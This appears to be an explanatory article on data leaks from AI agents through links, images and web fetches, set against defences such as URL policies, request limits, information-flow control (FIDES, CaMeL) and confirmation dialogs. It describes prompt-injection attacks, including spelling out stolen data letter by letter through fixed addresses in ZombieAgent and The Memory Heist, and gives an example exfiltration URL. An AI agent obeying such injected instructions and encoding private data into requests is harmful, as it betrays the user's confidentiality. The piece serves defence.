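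Even that rule would depend on who wrote the prompt. In the API, a user message is a request field that the developer's program fills in. Willison points out that many applications put outside text in this field. For example, a mail assistant might combine the employee's question with the full text of a supplier's email. Every link in the email then counts as an address from the user, including any that an attacker put there.

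Anthropic's *Web fetch 工具*, a later Chinese edition of the documentation, describes a different weakness in the second source. Some tools repeat what Claude sends them. A tool that runs code prints whatever the code tells it to, and an error message may quote the faulty input. If Claude builds an address from private data and such a tool repeats the address, it has appeared in a tool result, so the fetch tool accepts it by default.

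Anthropic's tool also refuses addresses that seem to contain a password or an API key, unless the same credential appears in the system prompt or in the text of a user message. This helps, but placing outside text in the user message weakens this check too. If the mail assistant puts an email containing a password there, the check no longer blocks addresses containing that password. The check also misses private information that doesn't look like a credential, such as a home city.

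### Spelling with fixed addresses

Both companies' rules prevent the agent from writing private data into an address, but the agent can still choose which of the permitted addresses to open. Suppose an attacker's site has one page for each letter. An agent that opens the pages for L, E, E, D and S has sent the attacker the word "Leeds" without changing any address. This is an extreme form of splitting data over several requests, since each request conveys only one character.

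Rehberger described this possibility in 2023, and he notes that OpenAI's paper acknowledges it. The security company Radware exploited it in an attack on ChatGPT called ZombieAgent. By then, OpenAI had stopped ChatGPT from adding parameters to an address, even when instructed to, so ChatGPT could only open addresses exactly as provided. The attack got around this by using addresses prepared in advance, as Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data* explains.

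Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes an email that contained hidden instructions and a list of addresses, one for each letter and digit and one for a space. When the user later asked ChatGPT to do something with Gmail, it read the email, found the private data and opened the addresses that spelled it out, one character at a time. The requests came from OpenAI's servers, so neither the user's browser nor a company firewall could have stopped them. Radware reports that an improved version succeeded every time, but doesn't say how many times it was tried.

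Leaking even short strings can do harm. In another demonstration, ChatGPT sent email addresses from the user's inbox to the attacker's server, which then emailed the same instructions to those addresses.

Radware reported the flaw on 26 September 2025, and OpenAI fixed it on 16 December. According to Ars Technica's *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, published in January 2026, ChatGPT now refuses to open a link from an email unless the link appears in a well-known public index or qualifies in another way. The attacker's list had passed the earlier check because it was in the email. To pass the new check, the attacker needs pages that a crawler has already recorded.

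That is harder but still possible. Rehberger observes that anyone with a fairly large website or blog probably has 36 indexed pages already, and the injected instructions can assign a letter or digit to each, whatever words its address contains.

According to dyb's *The Read-Only Lie*, Ayush Paul found a similar weakness in Claude and published it on 9 July 2026 under the title *The Memory Heist*. Paul built a website for an invented coffee shop. When Claude visited, the site claimed that Claude had to identify its user by moving through a directory letter by letter. Hackaday's *This Week In Security* notes that Claude was allowed to open links on pages it had reached through the user or a search. Each page could therefore supply the addresses for the next letter. The server's log recorded the path Claude took, which revealed data from Claude's memory of earlier conversations.

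Willison reports that Anthropic said it had already found the problem internally and paid no bounty. Its fix stopped the tool from following links in fetched pages, so an attacker can no longer use those pages to supply new addresses. Claude can still choose between addresses in search results, so some of the channel may remain if a search returns several pages from the attacker's site.

Developers who use the API shouldn't assume that they have the same protection. The Chinese edition of the documentation uses Claude Opus 5.5, a model released after the July fix, in its examples, yet it still lists earlier fetch results as a permitted source by default. A developer can narrow the sources in the tool's settings:

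```
"url_sources": {
  "client_tool_results": { "type": "none" },
  "server_tool_results": {
    "type": "only",
    "tools": [{ "type": "tool_reference", "name": "web_search" }]
  }
}
```

This configuration excludes the developer's own tools and all of Anthropic's other than web search, which the developer must also have enabled. Addresses in user messages still count as known, so the developer has to keep outside text out of those messages or turn off that source too. The settings also offer an `except` filter, which permits every tool but those named. The `only` filter is safer because a tool added later stays excluded.

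### How much fixed addresses can carry

If an attacker can distinguish $N$ different patterns of requests, those requests can reveal at most

$$\log_2 N \text{ bits}.$$

One bit is enough to answer one yes-or-no question. A choice among 36 addresses, one for each letter and digit, carries $\log_2 36$, or about 5.2 bits. If the agent can return to the same addresses any number of times and the attacker sees the order, each further request adds about 5.2 bits, so there is no upper limit on the total.

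Now suppose that the agent can open each address only once, and that it opens all 36. The attacker learns nothing from which addresses the agent visited, but their order can still carry information. There are $36!$ possible orders:

$$\log_2(36!) \approx 138 \text{ bits}.$$

Letting the agent stop early adds less than 1.5 bits to this limit. If the order is also hidden, only the set of visited addresses can carry information. Each address is either in the set or not, so there are $2^{36}$ possible sets, which can carry at most 36 bits.

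| Use of 36 fixed addresses | Patterns | Maximum leak |
|---|---|---|
| One request | $36$ | 5.2 bits |
| Ten requests, with repeats and visible order | $36^{10}$ | 51.7 bits |
| All 36 once each, with visible order | $36!$ | 138 bits |
| Each at most once, with hidden order | $2^{36}$ | 36 bits |

A random six-digit login code contains about 20 bits, so it fits even in the last row. A 128-bit encryption key would fit in the third row. These are upper limits, and some would be hard for a language model to reach because it would have to convert the key, for example, into an ordering of 36 addresses. An agent that can run code could do this easily.

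The attacker may also have far more than 36 addresses. Rehberger suggests using thousands, so that a page could stand for a whole word. With 4,096 pages, each request carries 12 bits. If the attacker's site has an indexed page for every large city, the attacker can learn where the user lives from a single request.

### Caching and a ban on repeat visits

Rehberger proposes two ways to make leaking data this way harder. The agent's software could cache each response for a few minutes, or prevent the agent from visiting the same full address twice in a session. He hadn't tested whether OpenAI already did either.

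Whether the agent caches responses or is banned from fetching an address twice in a session, the attacker's server receives only one request for each address. Spelling "Leeds" with one page per letter therefore fails at the second E. The ban is stronger because a cached response eventually expires, after which the agent can request the address again. But the ban is also more inconvenient for the user, who may want the agent to check a page again for a changed price.

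Over 36 requests, the ban lowers the maximum by only about a quarter, from about 186 bits to 138. Its main benefit is that the total can't keep growing unless the attacker provides more addresses.

Radware's researchers numbered the addresses by position to preserve the order of the characters, so the first character had its own set of pages, the second had another, and so on. For a block of $b$ characters, the attacker needs $36b$ addresses. Ten characters take 360 addresses, and the agent opens ten of them, each once. Because each address includes the position, the attacker can reconstruct the text even if the requests arrive out of order. Neither of Rehberger's proposals would reduce how much text an attacker could extract with such a list.

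They would still make the attack more expensive under OpenAI's rule, because the crawler has to have recorded all 360 pages. The rule places a much greater obstacle in the way of a site like Paul's, which creates new links at every step. If every page leads to 36 more, a tree that covers all strings of up to four characters has

$$36 + 36^2 + 36^3 + 36^4 = 1{,}727{,}604$$

pages, and a crawler is unlikely to record them all. Without an index, the server has to create only the pages that the agent asks for, and all of them are new, so a ban on repeat visits has no effect.

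Limiting the number of requests is often more effective than banning repeats. With $m$ known addresses, $k$ requests can leak roughly $k \log_2 m$ bits. Doubling the number of addresses adds one bit per request, while each additional request adds $\log_2 m$ bits. Anthropic's fetch tool can limit requests through its `max_uses` setting, which has no default value. With a limit of five requests, 36 addresses can leak about 26 bits, which is more than a login code but much less than a paragraph of an email.

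The limit applies to each turn, so it resets with the user's next message. Limits per session have the same problem over a longer period, since Radware showed that an injection could write instructions into ChatGPT's memory and make it repeat the theft in later chats. A research agent may also need to fetch dozens of pages for a legitimate task. A sensible limit would allow more requests in total but only a few to any unfamiliar domain, though an attacker could respond by using several domains.

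A stricter form of caching removes this channel. If the agent reads only copies that a crawler collected earlier, the attacker's server receives no request, so the attacker learns nothing from the agent's choices. OpenAI offers this in Lockdown Mode, an optional setting for people who handle sensitive data. According to OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT*, browsing in this mode uses only cached content, so no live requests leave the company's controlled network.

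The cache prevents leaks only if it is filled independently of the user's requests. An ordinary cache contacts the website the first time the agent asks for a page, and that first request is already a signal. Anthropic's fetch tool also caches pages by default, but Anthropic describes this as a performance feature and says it may change, so developers shouldn't rely on it to prevent leaks.

Lockdown Mode is inconvenient. According to OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, search results may be missing or out of date, ChatGPT may not show images from the web, and deep research and agent mode are unavailable. The mode also doesn't cover network access in Codex and leaves some connected apps available in managed workspaces, so OpenAI doesn't guarantee that it stops every leak. These limits seem reasonable for someone who works with confidential files and mostly needs older public information, but the mode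 would be a poor fit for tasks like booking a hotel.

### The page behind a known address

A match in OpenAI's index shows that an address was public, but not that the page is safe. OpenAI acknowledges that the page may still contain misleading or harmful instructions, or attempts to manipulate the user. Rehberger also notes that the rule blocks a way to steal data and is not presented as a defense against prompt injection.

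Attackers, like anyone else, can get their own pages into a public index. They can also add instructions after the crawler has recorded a harmless page, or use cloaking to hide the instructions from the crawler. In both cases, the address will still match the one in the index.

An agent that reads stored copies of pages won't see later changes until the crawler returns, but a copy can already contain hostile instructions when it is saved. OpenAI warns that prompt injections in cached pages and uploaded files can still affect ChatGPT's answers in Lockdown Mode. An agent that is also allowed to send mail or delete files could follow such instructions without requesting a suspicious address.

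## How should links be inspected, step by step?

An inspector needs to run several checks in a fixed order, because each check prevents a failure that the others can't detect. This procedure is for an assistant that writes answers in Markdown and can open web pages.

| Step | Failure it prevents | Cost |
|---|---|---|
| 1. Parse the text with the renderer's own parser | the inspector misses a link in an unfamiliar notation | a separate set-up for each renderer |
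| 2. List every destination, including images and HTML | a filter for links forgets images | some false alarms |
| 3. Canonicalise each address with the fetcher's own URL parser | the inspector approves a host that the fetcher never contacts | refusal of some malformed addresses that would have worked |
| 4. Apply the policy to the whole address | private data leaves through a permitted domain | delays and refusals for some legitimate links |
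| 5. Build the displayed text from the checked tree | a second parser finds a link in the leftovers | changed formatting |
| 6. Hold back links and images until their check ends | the browser sends a request while the model is still writing | images appear late |
| 7. Check again at the request and at every redirect | a tool call or redirect avoids the earlier checks | slower requests and a modified fetcher |

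### A harmless answer with three addresses

Suppose an employee asks her mail assistant about a supplier's invoice, and the model writes this:

```
Your [March invoice](https://Example.com:443/march?id=42) is due on Friday.

![Payment chart][c]

Questions? See www.example.org/help.

[c]: https://static.assistant.example/chart.png
```

The renderer follows GFM. Its parser produces this tree, shown here without the plain text:

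```
document
├─ paragraph
│  └─ link   "March invoice"         → https://Example.com:443/march?id=42
├─ paragraph
│  └─ image  "Payment chart"         → https://static.assistant.example/chart.png
└─ paragraph
   └─ link   "www.example.org/help"  → http://www.example.org/help
```

The parser has matched the image with its definition, added `http://` to the bare URL, and left the sentence's full stop out of the URL.

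The inspector has to use the same parser package as the renderer, in the same version and with the same settings. A port to another programming language isn't close enough. The JavaScript parser markdown-it disables HTML by default, whereas its Python port, markdown-it-py, enables it. This can hide an ordinary link:

```
<div>
[March invoice](https://example.com/march)
</div>
```

With HTML enabled, the parser passes all three lines through as HTML, where square brackets have no special meaning. With HTML disabled, it shows the tags as text and turns the middle line into a link. With default settings, a Python inspector would therefore find no link where a JavaScript renderer displays one. The Python port's documentation strongly recommends the `js-default` preset for text that users submit, and using that preset should also remove the mismatch.

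Some renderers let the developer run the check inside the parser. TanStack's *Security* describes a function that receives every link and image destination and its type, including destinations in reference definitions. An inspector that runs there doesn't need its own Markdown parser.

Next, the inspector canonicalises the addresses. A WHATWG parser puts the host in lower case and drops port 443, the default for `https`. The company in this example has three rules:

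- Images load automatically only if the application created their exact address on its own image server.
- A link opens directly if it leads to a known supplier and the same address appears in the supplier's email, so the model can't have added data to it.
- Any other link requires the employee's confirmation.

| Visible text | Sent when | Canonical address | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| March invoice | she clicks | `https://example.com/march?id=42` | open |
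| Payment chart | the answer appears | `https://static.assistant.example/chart.png` | load |
| www.example.org/help | she clicks | `http://www.example.org/help` | ask first |

### Building the answer from the tree

If the company controls the renderer, it can put the canonical addresses into the tree and display the answer directly from it. The text is then not parsed a second time, so nothing that the inspector did not detect can become a link.

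An answer that GitHub or another outside service will display has to become Markdown again. The application also can't show its own confirmation dialog there, so it has to decide about the help page in advance. Here it writes that address as code, which GFM doesn't turn into a link:

```
Your [March invoice](<https://example.com/march?id=42>) is due on Friday.

![Payment chart](<https://static.assistant.example/chart.png>)

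Questions? See `www.example.org/help`.
```

The reference definition is gone, and both active destinations use the same notation.

Socket's *markdown-to-markdown-sanitizer* describes an open-source package that automates this kind of rewriting. The package converts Markdown to HTML, cleans the HTML, converts the result back to Markdown, and replaces control characters in the text with character references, which can't start a link. It doesn't use backslashes for this because parsers handle them differently.

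The rewritten Markdown is hard for people to read. The documentation calls the method less secure than cleaning the final HTML, and recommends the package only when a third party renders the Markdown. The developers test the package's output with five renderers and 555 attempted bypasses, but they don't guarantee that it is secure.

Bare URLs need a separate test. The package doesn't replace full stops, so an address such as `www.example.com` might pass through unchanged and become a link in the final renderer. Even a character reference may not prevent this if the renderer searches for bare URLs after decoding the text.

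Bare URLs also cause trouble during streaming, because the host can change as more text arrives. A renderer may receive `https://example.com` first and then `.example.net/`. If it activates the link after the first piece, an approval for example.com could be applied to an address at example.net. The renderer should wait until the address has clearly ended, and the approval should apply only to that exact address. In the invoice answer, the chart's definition arrives last, so the employee sees a placeholder until then.

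### Checking again at the request

Checking the links in an agent's answer doesn't prevent its tools from leaking data when they open a page. Tenable's *Gemini Browsing Tool* describes an attack in which Gemini, Google's assistant, sent a user's saved information and location to an outside server by opening a page. Google's protections against leaks through Markdown and images didn't cover the browsing tool, and Gemini didn't ask for confirmation. Google has since blocked this route.

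Suppose the employee now asks the assistant to open the March invoice. The fetcher receives the canonical address, checks it and sends the request. The supplier's server replies with a redirect:

```
https://files.example.com/march.pdf?expires=1793000000&sig=9f3c71d0a8
```

The developer has to turn off automatic redirects so that the software can canonicalise each new address and apply the policy before the next request. A limit on the number of redirects prevents endless chains. In this case the fetcher can proceed because the new host belongs to the same supplier, and the new address came from the supplier's server in response to a request that contained no private data from the employee's mailbox.

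### Single-use, signed and rewritten links

An inspector should judge a link's address without requesting it, and examine the page only when the agent makes the real request, because opening a legitimate link can have side effects. A password reset link often works only once, so an inspector that opens it to find out where it leads can leave the employee with an expired link. Other links confirm an appointment or cancel a subscription as soon as someone opens them. The drawback of waiting is that nobody knows where a short link leads until the agent or the user opens it. An agent also shouldn't open such links just to summarise a message.

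The redirect to the invoice file is a signed link. The server calculates `sig` from the rest of the address and a secret key, and rejects the request if anyone has changed the address. The signature looks like a stolen password to a filter for random-looking values, so knowing where the address came from is more useful than measuring how random it looks. Canonicalisation can also break a signature, for example by sorting the query parameters. The fetcher's own parser is again the safest choice, since it makes only the changes the fetcher would make anyway.

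Signed links may give access to anyone who has them, so inspectors should keep them out of ordinary logs and not send them to outside reputation services.

Link-rewriting services cause a different problem. Many companies use a mail security product that replaces every address with one on its own domain, so that it can check the destination when someone clicks. The supplier's link might reach the assistant like this:

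```
https://links.example.org/check?u=https%3A%2F%2Fexample.com%2Fmarch%3Fid%3D42
```

Every link in the mailbox then has the same host. A model that compares the sender's domain with the link's domain will find a mismatch each time, and a list of permitted domains will accept all the links or none.

For link-rewriting services that the organisation uses, the inspector should extract the original address, canonicalise it and check it against the policy. It should also give the model the original address, but keep the rewritten link for the click so that the mail product's check still works. It shouldn't unwrap links from unknown hosts, because an attacker could imitate the format. If the service replaces the address with a short code, the inspector has to treat the link like any other short link.

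Google rewrites links in its own products. According to Embrace The Red, Google's programming notebook, Colab, puts `https://www.google.com/url?q=` in front of every clickable address, and Google shows a confirmation page before the user continues. Tenable's *The Trifecta* reports that links in Gemini's answers also go through a google.com address. The redirect protects a person who clicks, but another agent reading the link may mistake google.com for the destination.

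### Output controls at Google and Microsoft

Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025) describes two controls on Gemini's output. A Markdown sanitizer doesn't render images from outside addresses, and Google says this is why EchoLeak's image leak doesn't apply to Gemini. A second control checks links with Google Safe Browsing and removes suspicious ones. In an email summary, the user sees "suspicious link removed" in place of the address.

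The image rule is the stronger of these controls because it doesn't depend on recognising the attacker's domain. Its only drawback is that users can't see external images. Safe Browsing checks only a destination's reputation, so a newly registered domain may pass.

Gavish (2026), in *Google Workspace’s continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections*, describes a central policy engine through which Google controls link cleaning, user confirmation and the order in which Gemini may combine tools. Engineers can respond to a new attack by changing the engine's configuration, for instance by adding a regular expression that blocks a known pattern, which is faster than retraining a model. This is a sensible stopgap, although a regular expression applied to Markdown text has the same gaps as any simple filter. Gavish describes tests with and without each defence but publishes no success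 rates.

Microsoft also prefers deterministic defences, which are design choices that guarantee a particular attack will fail however the model behaves. After blocking the image leak that Rehberger had reported, the company took similar steps against certain untrusted links. But a fixed rule stops only the attacks it covers. Copilot's link filter was such a rule, and it missed reference-style links. A year later, in SearchLeak, the cleaning started too late.

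Microsoft may also be less consistent in practice than it describes. Checkmarx, a software security company, reports that Microsoft didn't commit to fixing an image leak in Copilot Chat that required no click, because it didn't consider the leak a vulnerability.

### Open-source renderers and their defaults

Open-source renderers offer link and image controls, but developers have to switch some of them on. Streamdown, a Markdown renderer, can restrict links and images to chosen addresses, according to its *Security* documentation. By default it cleans dangerous HTML but allows links and images from any domain, so a chatbot that uses the defaults would still load an attacker's image. The documentation advises stricter settings for untrusted content.

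Another example in the same documentation shows how to send every image through the developer's own server:

```
https://static.assistant.example/proxy?url=https://example.net/chart.png
```

If that server fetches any address it receives, attackers can exploit it as EchoLeak exploited the Teams proxy, so the server has to check the inner address itself.

Allowlist examples also need checking before use. The example in Streamdown's *Link Safety* tests whether an address starts with `https://` and a trusted host name, but leaves out the slash after the name, so if the trusted host is `example.com`, it also accepts `https://example.com.example.net/`. The renderer's separate list of permitted links may still block that address. The quick-start example for *harden-react-markdown* lists `https://docs.` as a permitted prefix. Depending on how the package compares addresses, that entry either matches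 no useful site or allows every domain that starts with `docs.`.

Socket's page recommends narrow prefixes such as `https://example.com/images/`, because a whole domain may contain open redirects. But the package doesn't resolve `/../`, which means "go up one folder", so a path that starts in the permitted folder can leave it. A WHATWG parser resolves `/../` before the comparison, but it leaves `..%2F` unchanged, and a server that decodes `%2F` before resolving the path may still go up a folder.

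### Network controls outside the model

The agent's maker should assume that an attacker will eventually get an address past the inspector. A domain list enforced when the agent makes a request, as in the test by Lan and colleagues, can still stop the leak. Enforcing the list on a separate machine makes it even harder to bypass.

In one design, the agent's machine has no direct route to the internet. The agent passes each address to a fetch service, which applies the policy, looks up the host and sends the request. Since the service looks up the host only after approving the address, private data in a subdomain can't leak through the lookup. Unlike an ordinary network proxy, the fetch service receives the full address even for HTTPS requests, so it can also apply rules to the path and query.

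This design adds another system to maintain, and it doesn't control requests from the employee's browser or a messaging app. Microsoft advises developers to give an agent only the privileges it needs and withdraw them after use. This helps with those requests too, because an agent that can't read the mailbox while it browses can't put email contents into URLs.

### Tracking where data came from

Information-flow control attaches labels to data and uses them to decide where the data may go. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, present FIDES, a Microsoft research design with two kinds of label. An integrity label records whether data comes from a trusted source, and a confidentiality label records who may read it. When the agent combines two pieces of data, only people who may read both may read the result:

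$$\text{readers}(a + b) = \text{readers}(a) \cap \text{readers}(b).$$

Suppose an injection makes the assistant build `https://example.net/p?city=Leeds`. Anyone may read the part before "Leeds", but only the employee and her manager may read the city, so the complete address is labeled as readable only by those two people. The owner of example.net isn't one of them, so the policy engine refuses the request. The decision doesn't depend on whether "Leeds" looks secret, and splitting the word into pieces doesn't help the attacker because each piece keeps the label.

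Any part of a model's input can affect what it writes, so once the model has read a stranger's email, the software has to treat its output as untrusted, and the agent can do very little. To avoid this, FIDES stores restricted data in variables and shows the main model only the variables' names. If the agent needs a detail from that data, a second model without tools extracts it in a fixed format.

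Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated office, banking and travel tasks with injected instructions. With appropriate policies, FIDES stopped every attack. Without policy checks, none of the designs compared, including FIDES, was secure. With the checks on, FIDES completed 8% more tasks than a basic agent when both used GPT-4o, and 16% more with OpenAI's o1. The basic agent presumably lost many tasks to the same checks, so these gains don't mean that security made the agent more useful. With the checks off, FIDES performed 6.3% worse than the basic agent because of its extra machinery.

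CaMeL (Debenedetti et al., 2025) separates the models more strictly. As *CaMeLoT* (2026) explains, a planning model receives only the user's request and writes a short program before any model reads the outside data. An interpreter runs the program, and a quarantined model extracts values from emails or pages. Each value carries a record of its source and permitted readers, and a policy checks this record before every tool call.

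An injection in the supplier's email can't add a step to the program. It can still make the quarantined model extract the wrong link, so the policies remain essential. *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (2026) tested CaMeL against attacks that corrupt the data an agent reads:

| Protection | Successful attacks |
|---|---|
| No defence | 49.1% |
| CaMeL's separate models, without policies | 25.0% |
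| CaMeL with policies, normal mode | 23.1% |
| CaMeL with policies, strict mode | 0% |

Strict mode also tracks implicit flows, in which private data influences a choice without appearing in the result. An agent that spells "Leeds" by opening fixed addresses leaks data this way. The researchers also had to extend CaMeL's policies to cover the final answer, where a linked image can send data out without any tool call. They caution that complete policies are much harder to write for real systems than for a benchmark.

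When *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) reran CaMeL, the policies blocked every attack, but the agent's usefulness collapsed. The same paper reports near-perfect security without this loss for another design, RANDORI, so the loss may be avoidable. CaMeL also uses more tokens, the units of text by which providers charge. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) tested it with GPT-4o and found that, for the median task, it used 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens as an undefended agent.

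Developers must also describe the format of each tool's results in advance, because the planning model writes its program before it sees any results. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) describes this as a modest, one-time job. That seems fair for a fixed set of office tools, but less so for arbitrary web pages.

No labelling scheme can fully protect a user who lets the attacker decide what the assistant does. If the employee asks the assistant to follow the instructions in a file exactly, an injected instruction in that file is part of the task. *The LLMbda Calculus* points out that several independent designs fail on such requests. Ma, Li and colleagues (2026), in *AutoDojo*, likewise found that attacks succeed much more often when the user names no action and defers to the content. "Open the March invoice" is therefore a safer request than "do what the supplier's email asks".

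### A language model as an extra checker

Exact rules can't detect that a page on an unfamiliar domain imitates the supplier's payment form. A language model often can, especially if the software queries it directly instead of relying on an agent that is in the middle of a task. The model doing this check should receive the canonical address, the registrable domain and facts such as the domain's age. It shouldn't have tools or access to private data.

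The checker should be able to block a link or send it for review, but not approve a link that the exact rules refuse. If $E$ is the set of addresses that pass the exact rules and $M$ the set that the model accepts, the agent may open only

$$E \cap M \subseteq E.$$

If the model cannot overrule the rules, an attacker who completely fools it can still do only what the rules permit. Otherwise, one persuasive sentence might be enough to get around them.

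Ma and colleagues show that a checker's test results can be misleading. PIGuard, a classifier that detects injected instructions, blocked every attack in a standard test with GPT-4o-mini, but 28.0% got through when another model rewrote the attacks using only information about which ones had succeeded. URLGuard's published results are incomplete in another way, because they leave out false alarms.

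False alarms matter because most links are harmless. Suppose that one email in 1,000 is phishing, and that a checker does as well as GPT-4o-mini did with Litvak's domain-comparison prompt, when it blocked 3.8% of harmless emails. Out of 10,000 emails, the checker would catch about 9 of the 10 phishing emails and flag about 380 harmless ones. If every flag produced a warning, the user would see roughly 40 false warnings for each correct one.

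### What a confirmation dialog has to show

User confirmation works only if people read the dialog. OpenAI argues that frequent warnings can train people to click through them, and Costa and colleagues warn of "confirmation fatigue". Their concern is plausible, but neither provides measurements that would show how many warnings are too many. Still, with 40 false warnings for each correct one, people could easily learn to ignore them.

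OpenAI's dialog warns the user that the link is unverified, shows the address, and lets the user copy or open it. This is a good start, but most people will understand little of a long address with encoded data, and OpenAI's checks no longer apply once the user copies the link into another browser.

For the help page in the invoice answer, a more informative dialog could look like this:

```
Open a page on example.org?

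Full address:   http://www.example.org/help
Link found in:  email from billing@example.com
Private data:   none found in the address

[ Don't open ]   [ Open once ]
```

The application should write the approval dialog's text from the canonical address and its own records, because an injection could influence a description written by the model. The dialog should show domain names with look-alike characters in their `xn--` form and name the final destination of a rewritten link. If the address contains private data, the dialog should show that data in readable form, so that the employee sees "Leeds" rather than an encoded string. Her approval should cover one request to this exact address, and a redirect to another site needs a new decision.

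The application should ask the user only when she has information that the software lacks, such as whether she expected a document from this supplier. It can refuse an address that contains a stolen password without asking her. Google's Gemini requires confirmation for risky actions such as deleting calendar events, and it lists the affected events first. After Google's defences have stopped an attack, Gemini just displays a notice, which requires no decision.

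In Microsoft Outlook, Copilot drafts an email but the user has to send it, which makes confirmation part of the task. This interrupts people less than a separate warning, since they would normally read a draft before sending it. The draft still has to show where its links lead and must not load outside images, or data could leak while the user is checking the text.
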